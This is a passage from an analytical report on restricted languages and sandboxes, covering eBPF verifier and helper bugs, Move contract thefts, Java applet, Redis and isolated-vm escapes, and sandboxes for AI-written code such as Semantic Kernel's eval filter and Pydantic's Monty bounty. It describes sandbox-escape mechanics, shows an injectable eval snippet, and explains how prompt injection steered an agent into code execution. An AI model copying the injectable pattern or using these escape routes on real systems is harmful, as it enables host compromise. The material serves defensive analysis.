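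| Curve and related pools, 2023 | $52 million lost after returns | language implementation: compiler | one slot for each lock name, and new contracts |
| Flow, 2025 | $3.9 million in counterfeit tokens | language implementation: runtime | stop values from passing as another type |
| Initia, 2026 | $2.7 million stolen | language implementation: virtual machine | correct the script cache |
| Move's missing path, 2023 | found by researchers | language implementation: verifier | include the jump at the end of a long function |
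| Crashes, endless loop and counter error in Move | found by researchers | language implementation: verifier and virtual machine | correct each fault in the shared code |
| Aptos Move flaw, 2026 | found by researchers | language implementation | correct Aptos's version of Move |
| Typus Finance, 2025 | $3.44 million stolen | program's own logic | check who is calling |
| Pawtato Finance, 2026 | game tokens created at will | program's own logic | check the value that the code required but ignored |
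| Lombard, Navi, Kuna Labs, SuiFrens, Cetus orders | found by auditors | program's own logic | one or two lines in each contract |

None of these cases was a host integration bug. A blockchain gives every contract the same fixed set of functions, so nobody chooses what to expose to each one, as the online shop does when it writes `refund`. The closest case is SuiFrens, where a contract's author exposed a helper function to strangers by mistake.

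Some of these classifications are debatable. Cetus itself maintained the arithmetic library, so one could call the library's error a mistake in the program's own logic. The Curve thefts required both a broken lock and a function that sent funds before updating its records, so fixing either one would have prevented them.

The table doesn't measure how common each kind of bug is, because large thefts and clever flaws attract detailed reports, while a small contract that doesn't check its caller may get none. Implementation flaws fill more rows than program logic, yet most findings in audits of Move contracts concern logic, validation and calculation. The sums of money are also a poor guide, since primitives come first only because of Cetus. Before May 2025, the language implementation would have come first.

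A list of thefts leaves out the bugs that the languages prevented. If Move's compiler rejected a contract that would have copied a coin, the programmer fixed it before deploying it, and no investigator wrote a report. The list shows where the remaining bugs were, but not how many more there would have been in a less restricted language.

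## What happened when kernels, browsers and databases ran restricted code?

Most of the robbed contracts had honest authors. Kernels, browsers and databases have faced a harder problem, because the person who writes the code may be the attacker. Prompt injection creates the same problem for AI agents. The best-documented case is the Linux kernel, which runs programs written in a restricted language called eBPF.

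### What the eBPF verifier checks

The kernel is the core of an operating system. It controls memory, files and network connections, so a faulty program inside it can crash the machine and a hostile one can take it over. Since 2014 Linux has supported loading small eBPF programs into the running kernel. Companies use them to filter traffic, spread load between servers and monitor performance.

Suppose somebody floods the online shop's server with junk traffic from a few addresses. An eBPF program can drop that traffic before the rest of the kernel spends any time on it. In Python-like notation:

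```
def on_packet(packet):
    if packet.length < 34:
        return PASS
    entry = lookup(blocked, packet.source)
    if entry is not None:
        return DROP
    return PASS
```

The first 34 bytes of a packet normally hold its headers, including the sender's address. `blocked` is a map, a table that eBPF programs share with ordinary software. The shop's staff fill it with addresses. `lookup` is a helper function, eBPF's name for a host function. Kernel developers write helpers in ordinary C.

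The author usually writes the program in C or Rust and compiles it to bytecode. At load time, the kernel's verifier traces the possible paths through the bytecode and records what each variable could contain at every step. Without the length test, one path would read an address from a packet too short to contain one, and the verifier would reject the program. If the program passes, a second compiler turns it into machine code.

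*Rex* (Jia, Qin and colleagues, 2025), a paper on an alternative to the verifier, describes the verifier's other rules. A program may access only memory that the kernel has made available to it, and must treat the data there as the right type. It must release every lock it takes, and may hold only one at a time. It must also finish, and use only a small amount of stack, the memory that holds a function's working data. These rules restrict computation and data, but they restrict authority much less, since a program that passes the verifier may still call powerful helpers.

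The verifier also rejects many safe programs. Because following every path takes time, it stops after a fixed number of instructions. A program with several branches inside a loop can exceed that limit even though it always finishes. *Rex* examines 72 changes that programmers made to three large eBPF projects only because the verifier had rejected a safe program. The most common workaround, in 27 cases, was to split the program into smaller ones. BMC, a cache that answers data requests from inside the kernel, should have needed two programs, but its developers had to write seven.

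Sometimes the compiler causes the rejection. In Cilium, a networking project, the compiler moved a memory address through a 32-bit register. The verifier then treated the address as an ordinary number and rejected the program's attempt to read from it. The programmers had to write that step in assembly language.

One proposed fix for the verifier's rejection of safe programs lets the programmer supply a mathematical proof when the verifier can't establish that a step is safe, and adds a checker to the kernel to confirm the proof. *Keel* (2026) reports several bugs in that checker that an attacker could have used to forge a proof and load an unsafe program.

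### Helpers as a way around the rules

When the language can't express an operation, kernel developers can also write it in C and offer it as a helper. *Kernel extension verification is untenable* (Jia, Sahu and colleagues, 2023), an earlier paper from the same group, argues that this practice undoes the verifier's work.

According to this argument, the verifier can analyse only small, simple programs. Users want programs that do more, so developers add helpers, roughly 50 every two years. The verifier checks the arguments that a program passes to a helper, but not the helper's own code. As programs hand more of their work to helpers, the verifier's approval covers less of what they do.

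The helper `bpf_loop`, for example, runs a piece of the program repeatedly. Developers added it because the verifier cannot easily check long loops. But that piece can call `bpf_loop` too, so if each level repeats a thousand times, three levels run the innermost code a billion times, much as nested macros multiply work in CEL. Jia and colleagues kept such a program running for 800 seconds while it held a lock that prevents the kernel from clearing away old data. They calculated that a more deeply nested version would run for millions of years. Strictly speaking, even that version would satisfy the verifier's intended guarantee that programs end.

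Helpers can break memory safety too. `bpf_sys_bpf` lets a program make some of the kernel's own management calls, and running it can involve more than 4,800 kernel functions. Its argument is a structure that contains memory addresses. The verifier checked that the structure was in valid memory but didn't check the addresses inside it. Jia and colleagues crashed the kernel by putting a null address in the structure. The flaw also let a program read any kernel memory. The researchers propose wrapping the helper in a Rust interface that accepts only valid addresses.

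They also searched the kernel's change log for security fixes from 2021 and 2022 and found 40.

| Kind of bug | In the verifier | In helpers |
|---|---|---|
| Access outside the permitted memory | 6 | 1 |
| Use of an empty address | 1 | 6 |
| Leak of kernel addresses | 5 | 0 |
| All others | 10 | 11 |
| Total | 22 | 18 |

These counts show that verified programs can reach plenty of faulty code, but not that most helpers exist because the language is too limited. Linux 5.18 had 249 helpers, and Jia and colleagues cite an estimate that a more expressive language could make 16 of them unnecessary, including `bpf_loop`. Most of the rest read or change something in the kernel, and a program in any language would need some such function, just as the shop's refund rule needs `refund`. The verifier also had more bugs than all the helpers together.

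Helpers can cause problems in combination even if each one is correct. The verifier allows each program 512 bytes of stack but doesn't count the stack that helpers use. A helper may also call a kernel function to which somebody has attached another eBPF program, and that program may call a helper too. Chintamaneni, Somaraju and Williams (2024), in *Unsafe kernel extension composition via BPF program nesting*, explain that enough nesting overflows the kernel's stack, even though every program passed the verifier. They propose that the verifier use a chart of what each helper calls and how much stack those calls need.

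### Over a hundred memory bugs in a year

Huang, Sampson and colleagues (2025) review memory safety in eBPF in *SoK* and report that people found over 100 memory-error bugs in the eBPF subsystem in 2024. They write that 45 of these were still unfixed, but another passage counts those 45 among the 169 bugs found since 2023. Many of the bug reports come from syzbot, an automated service that runs generated programs on the kernel and reports the ones that cause errors.

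Huang and colleagues studied 102 flaws that came with a working demonstration, and sorted the causes into three groups.

In some cases the verifier's checks were wrong. To save time, the verifier skips a path that looks equivalent to one it has already approved. Because of one flaw from 2023, it did not record that a memory address depended on an offset stored elsewhere. Suppose a program owns a 64-byte block and uses it at offset 8 on one path and offset 128 on another. After approving the path with offset 8, the verifier could skip the other, and the program would access memory outside its block. The fix records the dependency, so the two paths no longer look equivalent.

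In other cases the verifier lacked a check. A program can borrow a block of memory from a buffer and return it through a helper. The verifier checked that the address came from a borrowed block, but not that it still pointed inside that block. A hostile program could borrow 64 bytes, shift the address by 128, and make the helper treat unrelated data as its own records. The fix is to reject any address that the program has shifted.

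The remaining flaws were in code that the verifier doesn't examine. One lookup function could return a table entry that nobody had filled in, and the program would then use whatever bytes were there.

Huang and colleagues generally hold the verifier responsible, because every one of these programs got past it. *eBPF Security in the Wild* (Chen, Ming and colleagues, 2026) instead sorts bugs by the component that failed. It found the largest share in the runtime, meaning the helpers, maps and kernel objects that programs use, and fewer in the verifier and the compiler that produces machine code. The study also covers timing errors between programs running at the same time, which Huang and colleagues leave out. Whether the unfilled table entry counts as a verifier bug or a primitive bug depends on which of them should have checked it.

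The totals also rise when people search harder. TechSpot (2026) reports that the number of kernel vulnerabilities fixed in each release rose from roughly 500 to nearly 2,000 as people began using AI tools to find them. Some of the tools' findings hardly matter. Starovoitov (2026), an eBPF maintainer, said that three in four of the AI-generated patches he sees are wrong, and that the maintainers will not fix a bug that appears only when someone adds an artificial delay to the kernel. The backlog may also have shrunk. The February 2026 report from syzbot (2026) lists 25 open issues and 318 fixed ones, and it covers more than memory errors.

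### Who may load a program

Supporters of eBPF have a strong reply to these counts, because ordinary users usually can't load eBPF programs. Linux used to let them load some kinds, but a kernel setting now controls this. According to Sysctl Explorer's *unprivileged_bpf_disabled*, whoever builds the kernel can make refusal the default, and an administrator can make it irreversible until the machine restarts. According to Jia and colleagues in *Rex*, the major Linux distributions have moved away from unprivileged loading.

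eBPF Docs' *BPF Token* explains that since Linux 5.8, a process needs one privilege to load eBPF programs and another if the programs handle network traffic. Linux calls these privileges "capabilities", but each one covers a whole class of actions rather than a particular resource.

The *Rex* paper gives three reasons why Linux gave up on running eBPF programs from untrusted users. First, bugs keep appearing in the verifier. Second, eBPF's developers decided to assume that somebody knows what each program is for, whereas a browser has to run scripts whose purpose nobody has checked. Third, a family of hardware weaknesses called Spectre can let a program leak kernel memory even if it obeys every rule of its language. Processors save time by guessing which branch a program will take and running ahead. They discard the results of a wrong guess, but traces remain in the processor's cache, and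 a program can recover secrets by timing its own reads. The known defences slow programs down.

The reply is correct, but accepting it means giving up much of the original hope. The kernel has one of the most heavily checked restricted languages in use, yet the kernel's maintainers don't trust that language to contain a hostile author's code. In *Re*, a message to the kernel's mailing lists, Google engineer Żenczykowski (2026) says that "allowing random apps any access to eBPF is a recipe for disaster". He wanted a way to block new eBPF programs after a device has started, even from processes with high privileges.

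The verifier is still useful against honest mistakes. Huang and colleagues ran an independent analysis that couldn't prove the safety of between 1.6% and 3.7% of the memory operations in public eBPF programs, compared with 8.8% in ordinary C programs. An operation that the tool can't prove safe isn't necessarily a bug, and eBPF programs are tiny and rarely manage memory for themselves, so the verifier may not account for the whole difference. But an administrator who forgets the length test in the traffic filter gets an error message, while the same mistake in an ordinary kernel module could crash the server.

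The eBPF verifier protects the kernel but doesn't ensure that programs work as intended. *Heimdall* (2026) found 137 places in 115 eBPF programs where the code ignored an error returned by a helper function. Such a program may go on to use a buffer that the helper never filled and give its users false information. The verifier accepts this because it doesn't endanger the kernel.

### Rex and KrakenGuard

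Researchers have proposed opposite remedies. Rex gives programmers a more expressive language, while KrakenGuard leaves the language alone and restricts each program's authority.

Rex removes the verifier. Programmers write in safe Rust, and the compiler rejects `unsafe` blocks. Some properties are hard to establish before a program runs, so Rex checks them during the run. It stops any program that reads past the end of a block of memory, and a timer stops any program that takes too long. A stopped program might still hold a lock, so Rex records each resource as the program acquires it and releases any the program still holds when it stops.

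This lets Rex drop the limits on loops and program size, along with `bpf_loop` and the helpers that only compare or convert text. Jia and colleagues rewrote BMC in Rex. The new version has 326 lines, compared with 513 lines spread over seven eBPF programs, and it handled 1.98 million requests a second, slightly more than the original's 1.92 million. Some small operations became slower, such as taking and releasing a lock, which takes 183 nanoseconds in Rex and 130 in eBPF.

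Rex still relies on much of the same C code. It wraps the remaining helpers in Rust interfaces that check types and sizes, but a program can still reach a bug deeper inside a helper. The kernel also stops examining programs, so it has to trust whoever compiled them and the Rust compiler, which Jia and colleagues acknowledge is larger than the verifier. They designed Rex for programs that an administrator chooses to load, and don't claim it would contain code from a hostile author.

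*KrakenGuard* (Patel, Buhl-Nielsen and colleagues, 2026) describes attacks that need no verifier bug, including one against Kubernetes. Kubernetes keeps an agent on every machine that reads instructions about what to run there. A hostile eBPF program can wait until the agent reads its instructions, then replace them with the attacker's by using two helpers, one that writes into another program's memory and one that changes the result a kernel function returns. The machine then starts a program with an administrator's powers. Every step obeys the verifier's rules, and both helpers work as documented.

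KrakenGuard runs outside the kernel and loads programs for users who lack the privilege to load them. An administrator writes a policy that lists the helpers a program may call, the maps it may read or change, the bytes of input it may touch and the results it may return. The shop's traffic filter would need permission to read 34 bytes of input and one map, and to return PASS or DROP. KrakenGuard checks every path through the program and blocks it from loading if any path breaks the policy. With a policy that left out the two dangerous helpers, KrakenGuard stopped the Kubernetes attack after about a quarter of a second of analysis.

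Patel and colleagues also tested three programs that exploit old flaws in the verifier, including the one with the shifted address. KrakenGuard rejected all three because each tried to reach memory outside its permitted ranges. Policies can also depend on a program's earlier actions. For example, a policy can forbid a program from altering a packet and sending it out after the program has read a table of secrets.

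KrakenGuard rejects any program that it can't analyse in time. It couldn't finish analysing BMC within a few minutes, because one of BMC's programs branches on a number calculated from a packet's contents. KrakenGuard also relies on hand-written models of the helpers, which somebody has to update for each kernel version, and it would miss any bug that is in the real helper but not in the model. The administrator must also get the policy right.

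| | eBPF verifier | Rex | KrakenGuard, on top of eBPF |
|---|---|---|---|
| Computation | limits on loops and size | no such limits, but a timer | eBPF's limits, and the analysis must finish |
| Data | checks before loading | the Rust compiler, and checks during the run | eBPF's checks, and limits on which bytes |
| Authority | depends on the type of program and the loader's privileges | the same helpers, minus a few | only what the policy lists |
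| Code that must be correct | verifier, second compiler, helpers | Rust compiler, Rex, helpers | eBPF's code, and KrakenGuard's analysis and models |

A kernel could not easily combine KrakenGuard with Rex. KrakenGuard can check every path in most programs only because the verifier already requires them to be small and simple. Rex would let programmers write programs that no such tool could analyse completely. Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn described this trade-off. Here, the limits on computation are useful mainly because they make it possible to check a program's authority.

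Linux developers are also working on finer control over eBPF permissions. A privileged process can already delegate some eBPF functions to a container, and *BPF-RBACd* (Høiland-Jørgensen, 2026) describes a system service that grants such permissions to individual applications.

### Java, Redis and isolated-vm

Browsers once ran Java applets, which were programs supplied by web pages. A verifier checked each applet's bytecode, and a security manager decided whether code had permission to open a file or connection. Applets could also call Java's huge standard library, which had full permissions. In August 2012, attackers exploited a library method that fetched internal classes for any caller, including applets with no right to them. One of those classes let an applet rewrite the record of its own permissions. The fault was in the primitives available to applets, and the fix made the library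 check the caller. Similar flaws kept appearing, browser makers dropped support for the Java plug-in, and Oracle, which maintains Java, eventually removed the plug-in.

Redis is a database that lets users run scripts on its server in Lua, a small general-purpose language. Its developers had withheld Lua's functions for opening files, but the Lua interpreter still had a memory flaw for about 13 years, until they fixed it in October 2025. While reading a new script, the interpreter stored the script's name in memory but didn't mark that memory as in use. Lua automatically frees memory that nothing is using, so it could free the name while the interpreter still needed it. A hostile script could then fill the freed memory with its own data and try to take over the server. The fix marks the name as in use until the interpreter has finished reading the script. Administrators who couldn't install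 the fix yet could protect their servers by forbidding users to run scripts.

The isolated-vm library runs untrusted JavaScript inside an application. Several products, including the office automation tool n8n, use it to run code that customers or AI models write. The library relies on V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine, which can give each script a separate region of memory called an isolate. An older library, vm2, was designed to separate scripts from the application within a single region, and researchers documented more than twenty escapes from it.

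Staicu (2026), in *GHSA-864f-rcv7-6rh4*, describes a sandbox escape from isolated-vm that left V8's separation intact. Scripts and the host can't share objects, so the library copies data between them. To avoid copying large blocks of memory, a script can list blocks to hand over whole. The C++ code that did this went through the list twice:

```
for item in transfer_list:
    check_is_memory_block(item)
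for item in transfer_list:
    hand_over(item)            # reads the list again, without a check
```

In JavaScript, reading an entry in a list can run a function, and that function can return something different each time. A hostile script could therefore supply a real block to the loop that checks the entries and a plain number to the loop that hands them over. The C++ code then treated the number as a memory address. Staicu's firm, Endor Labs, developed this into an exploit that let a script choose which code the host application ran next. The script needed only one reference to a host object, which is how a host usually gives a script anything. The maintainer's fix, in versions 7.0.1 and 6.2.0, prevents any JavaScript from running during the copy, so the list can't change between the two loops.

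### What separates the cases

In all these systems, the attacker wrote code that the language accepted and used it to trigger a bug in the surrounding software. A less expressive language would have helped in some of these cases but not in others.

Restricting the language would have helped isolated-vm. If scripts could pass only plain data, reading a list twice would give the same result both times, and the fix imposes that restriction during the copy. It would have done little for Redis, because the fault was in the code that reads a script before running it. Removing file access from Lua didn't affect that code, although a much simpler language would have needed less of it. For Java applets, shrinking the library would have helped more than restricting the language.

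eBPF is the awkward case, because the restrictions themselves need a large and complicated program to enforce them. According to Huang and colleagues, the verifier had grown to more than 22,000 lines by Linux 6.11, eleven times its original size. A language like CEL avoids this cost because its programs have no way to name a memory address, so nothing has to check how they use one. The kernel can't copy that solution completely, since its users want programs that handle raw packets at full speed.

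The maintainers of Redis and isolated-vm fixed the faults and still accept scripts, while Linux maintainers and browser makers mostly stopped accepting such programs from strangers. Hosts that run AI agents will find it hard to shut out strangers this way, because their own model writes the code and an attacker can influence it just by sending a refund request.

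## For AI agents, is a new small interpreter safer than a filtered full language?

An AI agent doesn't have to write programs. In the simpler arrangement, known as tool calling, the model asks for one host function at a time and reads each result before choosing the next step. Suppose the shop's agent must go through 200 refund requests and pay those under $50 from customers with fewer than three earlier refunds. It could need one call for the list, up to 200 for the customers' histories and up to 200 for the payments. Or it could write one program:

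```
paid = 0
for order in refund_requests():
    if order.total < 50 and earlier_refunds(order.customer) < 3:
        refund(order.id, order.total)
        paid = paid + 1
print(paid)
```

The model then reads a single number. The text of the requests, where an attacker may have hidden instructions, never has to reach it.

Pydantic's *Agent Sandboxes* page reports an October 2026 comparison of 5,276 runs of five applications on eight models. On long tasks, writing code raised the success rate of seven models, and the eighth succeeded every time with or without it. The weakest model gained most, from 14% to 58%. Token use, which largely determines the cost, fell for every model, by 9% to 70%. Pydantic sells a service for running such code and chose the test applications, so other workloads may gain less.

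When an AI agent writes code, the host has to run a program that nobody has reviewed. Models write Python fluently, so hosts usually want to accept Python or something close to it. They can keep the ordinary Python interpreter and filter out dangerous code, or use a new interpreter that supports only part of the language.

### A hotel search that could start any program

In May 2026 Microsoft described what went wrong with a filter in Semantic Kernel, its open-source framework for building agents. Its researchers built an agent that finds hotels. When a customer asked for hotels in Paris, the model called a search function with the city as its argument, and the framework narrowed the list roughly like this:

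```
text = "lambda x: x.city == '" + city + "'"
keep = eval(text)
```

`lambda x:` begins a small unnamed function, which here takes a hotel and returns true or false, and `eval` runs the text as code. A city name like "Paris" is harmless, but one that contains a quotation mark ends the quoted text early, and Python treats the rest as code. This is the same kind of flaw as SQL injection. The model supplied the city, and a prompt injection could make it supply any text. The researchers started the calculator on their machine with one message, and an attacker could have started any other program the same way.

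Semantic Kernel's developers had foreseen this danger and added three defences. The text had to be a single `lambda` expression, which ruled out import statements and class definitions. A checker searched the expression's syntax tree for forbidden names, such as `eval`, `exec` and `open`. The expression also ran without Python's built-in functions, so a dangerous name the checker missed should have been useless.

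The checker used Python's own parser, so it avoided the mismatch that had once let text past PostgreSQL's filter. The list of names failed because of how Python connects its objects. Every value, even an empty tuple (a list that cannot change), links to its class, and each class links to its parents. All classes descend from one common ancestor, which can list its descendants. A program can therefore start from an empty tuple, go up to that ancestor, and reach a large share of the classes in memory. One of these classes can load modules, including one that starts other programs.

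Removing the built-in functions made no difference, because this route doesn't need them. Requiring a single expression didn't help either, because an expression can be any length. Microsoft's researchers used four names that were missing from the blocklist. They also noticed that the checker ignored look-ups in square brackets, which could have let an attacker use names that were on the blocklist.

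Adding the four names to the blocklist would have closed one route. An agent's process usually contains many libraries, each with its own classes and functions, and a blocklist has to close every route through all of them. Installing a new library may also open a route that the existing blocklist doesn't cover.

### What the allowlist changed

The repaired checker, in version 1.39.4 of the Python package, accepts only listed kinds of syntax, such as comparisons, Boolean logic, arithmetic and literal values. An expression may call only listed functions, and the only bare name it may use is the one for the record under test (`x` in the example).

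The filter still uses one blocklist. It has to allow attributes such as `x.city`, so the developers separately forbid the attributes that lead from an object to its class. A gap in this list would matter less than a gap in the old one, because an attacker would usually also have to call a function that the filter doesn't permit.

These rules turn the filter into a small language much like CEL. Python still evaluates the expression, but the expression can access very little of Python. This restriction is much stronger than the old one and doesn't limit hotel searches.

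Two smaller problems could survive the allowlist. First, if the framework still pastes the city into the filter text, a crafted city name could add a condition that is true for every record. In a hotel search this would only lengthen the list of results, but if the filter were all that kept customers from reading each other's orders, it would expose every order. Second, if the permitted arithmetic includes powers, a short expression can require computing a number so large that the search hangs.

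A host that needs only this comparison can avoid both problems by leaving out `eval`:

```
keep = lambda x: x.city == city
```

Here the developer writes the code and the city remains a value, so nothing that a customer types can become part of the program.

Microsoft disclosed this flaw, CVE-2026-26030, together with CVE-2026-25592, which arose because the framework offered the model a file-writing function by mistake.

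### Other filters and enclosures

Blocklists have failed in other AI tools too. Developers often distribute models in pickle, Python's format for saving objects, and loading a pickle file can call functions. Picklescan looks for unsafe function names in these files before anyone loads them. According to OSV's *GHSA-hgrh-qx5j-jfwx* (2025), Picklescan's blocklist lacked `pty.spawn`, a standard Python function that starts a program. GCVE, a public vulnerability database, has an advisory about the same function for Fickling, another tool that checks pickle files.

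A language can sound restricted and still have the same problem. TeamCity, a server that builds and tests software, lets users write its settings in a domain-specific language (DSL) based on Kotlin. The DSL is a library for Kotlin, a general-purpose language, so a settings file is a Kotlin program that can do far more than define settings. In September 2026, GCVE listed a sandbox escape through the DSL and classified the cause as an incomplete list of forbidden inputs.

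Filters are still useful against mistakes. Hermetic's *Threat Model* describes a Python sandbox that runs inside the host's process, and states that the sandbox "is not a security boundary". Its developers recommend it for catching non-malicious misbehavior by libraries and language models, such as contacting a server during a test that should run offline.

A host can also leave Python unfiltered and isolate the whole interpreter. Pydantic's mcp-run-python did this by running Pyodide, a version of the standard Python interpreter compiled to WebAssembly, inside a JavaScript program. Pyodide lets Python code use JavaScript objects, and mcp-run-python did not block this access. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-25905* (2026), any Python code could use it to change the surrounding JavaScript environment and take over the server.

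The same tool also let Python code contact the machine it ran on, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-25904* (2026). If the shop had an administration page that trusted any request from its own computer, the untrusted code could have used that page. Both flaws were host integration bugs. The attacker didn't need a fault in Python or WebAssembly, because the tool had given the code more access than it needed.

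### Monty: an interpreter without the dangerous parts

Pydantic took the opposite approach with Monty, a new interpreter written in Rust that runs part of the Python language. Hopper (2026) reported its release in early February, the same month GitLab published the two advisories. Monty uses a parser from Ruff, a tool that checks Python code, but runs programs on its own virtual machine and contains none of the standard interpreter's C code.

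In ordinary Python, the code that opens files is always in memory, and a filter has to block every route to it. Monty's interpreter contains no code that opens files. When a program calls `open`, the interpreter pauses and gives the host a description of the request, and a separate component on the host's side decides what to do.

Similarly, if a program uses a name that it hasn't defined, Monty looks it up in a table that the host supplied. The shop's table might contain `refund_requests`, `earlier_refunds` and `refund`. The six-line program would then run, while a program that called `send_email` would stop with an error. A host can also pass in an object and list which of its attributes and methods a program may use. These lists are empty by default.

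A program needs no permission to do two things: read the clock and seed its random-number generator from the operating system's source of randomness. Reading the clock gives a program little power, but some attacks recover secrets by timing operations, so hosts can freeze the clock.

Monty now supports `eval` and `exec`, two of the names on Semantic Kernel's list. Code passed to them runs in the same interpreter, with the same limits and the same few host functions, so it can't do anything the original program couldn't.

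The interpreter also limits time and memory. For example, the expression `'x' * 10**12` would create a string of a trillion characters, and Monty reports an error before trying to allocate it. Monty's *Security model* page warns that none of these protections makes a host function safe, because host functions run with the host's full authority.

The design looked sound to at least one outside reviewer, the software developer Simon Willison, who asked Anthropic's Claude Code to examine a release in May 2026. He reported in *pydantic-monty investigation* (2026) that unsupported features and missing resources generally produced ordinary errors and did not reach the host. But a memory bug can break any design that depends on the interpreter being correct, and Pydantic had already paid someone for finding such a bug.

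### Round 1: an escape in under 48 hours

On 20 April 2026 Pydantic offered $5,000 to anyone who could use Monty to read a secret on a public test server. The server held one secret in a file and another in an environment variable, a setting that the operating system passes to a program. It received nearly 1.5 million requests from about 650 internet addresses. In less than 48 hours, Owen Kwan of the security firm Veria Labs ran his own code on the server and read the environment variable. Pydantic later said he had combined two bugs.

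The first was in the way Monty reuses memory. Like standard Python, it counts the references to each object and frees the object when the count reaches zero. Two lists that contain each other keep each other's counts above zero, so Monty also has a garbage collector. The collector starts from objects known to be in use, called roots, follows every reference from them, and frees whatever it hasn't reached. If its list of roots is incomplete, the collector can free an object that the program still needs.

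Monty's developers had forgotten a list that was in the middle of being sorted. Python programmers can supply a function that decides the order:

```
orders.sort(key=urgency)
```

Monty calls `urgency` during the sort. A hostile version of that function could trigger the garbage collector, which would free the list. The function could then fill the freed memory with bytes of the attacker's choice. When it returned, Monty would continue sorting and treat those bytes as its own records of a list.

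The second bug let this substitution go unnoticed. Rust normally lets code change a value only while nothing else is using it. Python objects refer to each other so freely that this rule is hard to satisfy. Rust has standard types that check the rule while the program runs, but Pydantic's engineers judged them too slow and complicated. They wrote their own mechanism in `unsafe` code, which relied on an object never changing its type.

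The engineers had documented their assumptions and run the code under Miri, a tool that checks for errors in unsafe Rust, but they hadn't considered that a faulty collector could replace a list with something else. If they had used safe Rust, Monty would probably have detected the wrong type and crashed. An attacker could then have interrupted the service but almost certainly not taken control of it.

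Version 0.0.16 fixed the bug by adding to the roots every object that the unsafe code depends on. Pydantic also reviewed its other unsafe code, but said in May that the collector's design still didn't rule out another missing root.

Redis's Lua interpreter had almost the same bug, but this one lasted about three months at most instead of 13 years. The attack also resembles Mallory's theft from Fund, because an operation handed control to untrusted code before finishing its own work. Removing custom sort functions from Monty's language would have blocked this attack, but the faulty collector could still have freed other objects too early.

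The test server had a separate fault in its simulated filesystem. Somebody wrote a fake secret to the file's path, and other visitors read it and thought they had won. One of Pydantic's developers said he had misused a confusing interface that he had designed. The company paid Stanislav Fort of the security firm AISLE $300 for reporting weaknesses in this filesystem. The fault was in the host integration, so a perfect interpreter would not have prevented it.

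### Rounds 2 and 3, and version 1

Round 2 began on 30 May with a $10,000 reward from Pydantic and two companies that use Monty in their products, Hugging Face and Prefect. Nobody escaped or read either secret. According to Pydantic's *Hack Monty Round 3 & Round 2 results*, participants did report crashes, gaps in the resource limits and differences from standard Python.

Round 3 ran through August with a reward of up to $20,000. Participants connected to a network service that gave each a separate Monty process with 10 MiB of memory and five seconds of running time. According to Pydantic's *Hack Monty* page, the service had no second sandbox, so anyone who broke Monty would have reached the server. Pydantic published the outcomes of the first two rounds, but its product page gives only the dates of the third.

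Pydantic released a stable version of Monty after round 3, as planned. Earlier releases carried a warning that Monty was experimental. Version 1.7.0, released on 24 November 2026, is marked "Production/Stable", and Pydantic presents it as a sandbox for code written by AI. The company now runs a permanent bug bounty programme.

### What an unclaimed bounty shows

Round 2 lasted about two months, so somebody would almost certainly have found another bug as easy to find as the one in round 1. But at the same level of effort, a bug a hundred times harder would take about 200 days to find on average, and would have had roughly a 74% chance of surviving round 2. This estimate relies on a single escape, and the effort in the two rounds may have differed. Still, two months without an escape can rule out easy bugs while providing little evidence about hard ones.

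The number of requests is a poor guide to effort. In round 1 the average was about 2,300 requests per address, which suggests that many people were running automated searches. Kwan's attack needed a sort, a hostile function and a garbage collection at the right moment, a combination that random programs seldom contain. When Pydantic announced round 2, it acknowledged that 1.5 million requests had not covered everything an attacker could try.

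Money also affects what people report. Someone who can escape from Monty might earn more by robbing a company that uses it than by reporting the escape for $10,000. Google's rewards for flaws in Chrome's V8 engine have reached $62,000. Round 2 also did not pay for crashes, although a crash can be the first sign of a memory bug.

Finally, each round tested the version available at the time. Pydantic keeps adding Python features at users' request, and each one adds code that participants in earlier rounds never attacked.

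Even so, the three designs fail in different ways:

| | Semantic Kernel's filter before the fix | The same filter after the fix | Monty |
|---|---|---|---|
| What a program can express | any single Python expression without a forbidden name | comparisons, logic, arithmetic and a few calls | a large part of Python |
| What separates it from the host | a list of forbidden names | a list of permitted syntax and functions | no code for reaching the host, except through what the host supplies |
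| What an attacker needs | one route that the list misses | a mistake in the checker or in a permitted operation | a memory bug and the skill to exploit it |
| What can weaken it later | any new library | an addition to the allowlist | any new feature in the interpreter |

Monty is clearly safer than the old filter. An attacker needs more skill to exploit a memory bug than to find a name missing from the filter's list, and Monty's developers can remove a memory bug by correcting one fault. The repaired filter is probably at least as safe as Monty, because it allows much less and depends on a well-tested interpreter for a few simple operations. But it could not run the six-line refund program. A host that needs loops and function calls would have to permit more of Python, and each addition would make the filter harder to get right.

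### Moving the interpreter out of the application

At first, Monty ran inside the application that used it. Prefect gave the drawback as its reason for paying half of round 2's reward: "Embedded also means a sandbox escape is a host compromise." An operating system gives each process its own memory, but an interpreter inside the shop's process shares the memory that holds the shop's database password and payment account key. An attacker who takes over the interpreter no longer needs `refund`, because the payment key can send money anywhere.

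By August, Pydantic had moved Monty into a separate worker process, mostly for reliability. A memory error now kills the worker but leaves the application running. The application can also measure the worker's memory use accurately and stop a worker that ignores its time limit.

The change also makes an escape less useful to an attacker. Workers start with an empty environment, so the variable that Kwan read in round 1 would be missing. The application treats every message from a worker as untrusted, because an attacker may have taken over the worker.

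But a separate process is a weak barrier by itself. Monty adds no container, virtual machine or filter on the system calls a worker can make. Pydantic's *Worker execution* notes describe an escape as "arbitrary native code running in the worker". Such code can usually open any file or network connection that the worker's user account allows. If the shop keeps its payment key in a file this account can read, the attacker can still get it. The package's description says "your process is never at risk", which is reasonable for crashes but too strong for escapes.

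By default, Monty also reuses each worker for up to 1,000 sessions, so an attacker who takes one over might see data from hundreds of later customers. Pydantic advises replacing the worker after every session if a host's users don't trust one another.

Other agent frameworks let the host choose the barrier. *EFFGEN* (Srivastava, Hussain and colleagues, 2026) describes a framework for agents that run on small language models. Its code executor can use a plain subprocess, a Docker container or Firecracker. A subprocess has its own memory. A container normally also has its own view of the files and network, but shares the host's kernel. Firecracker starts a small virtual machine with its own kernel, so an attacker would have to break out of that too. All three can run ordinary Python, with the barrier containing the code instead of a filter.

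A host can also put a small interpreter inside a second sandbox. *Running Python code in a sandbox with MicroPython and WASM* (Willison, 2026) presents an early version of this design, which runs a compact Python interpreter inside WebAssembly. An attacker who corrupts the interpreter's memory still needs another bug, in the WebAssembly engine or in a host function, to get out of the WebAssembly module. The outer layer protects the host only if the host doesn't open a way through it, as the failure of mcp-run-python shows.

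Speed is the usual argument against stronger barriers. Monty's developers compared the time to create a sandbox and run ten short commands in it:

| Sandbox | Time |
|---|---|
| Monty on the same machine | 1.2 ms |
| Monty as a remote service | 6.6 ms |
| WebAssembly | 200 ms |
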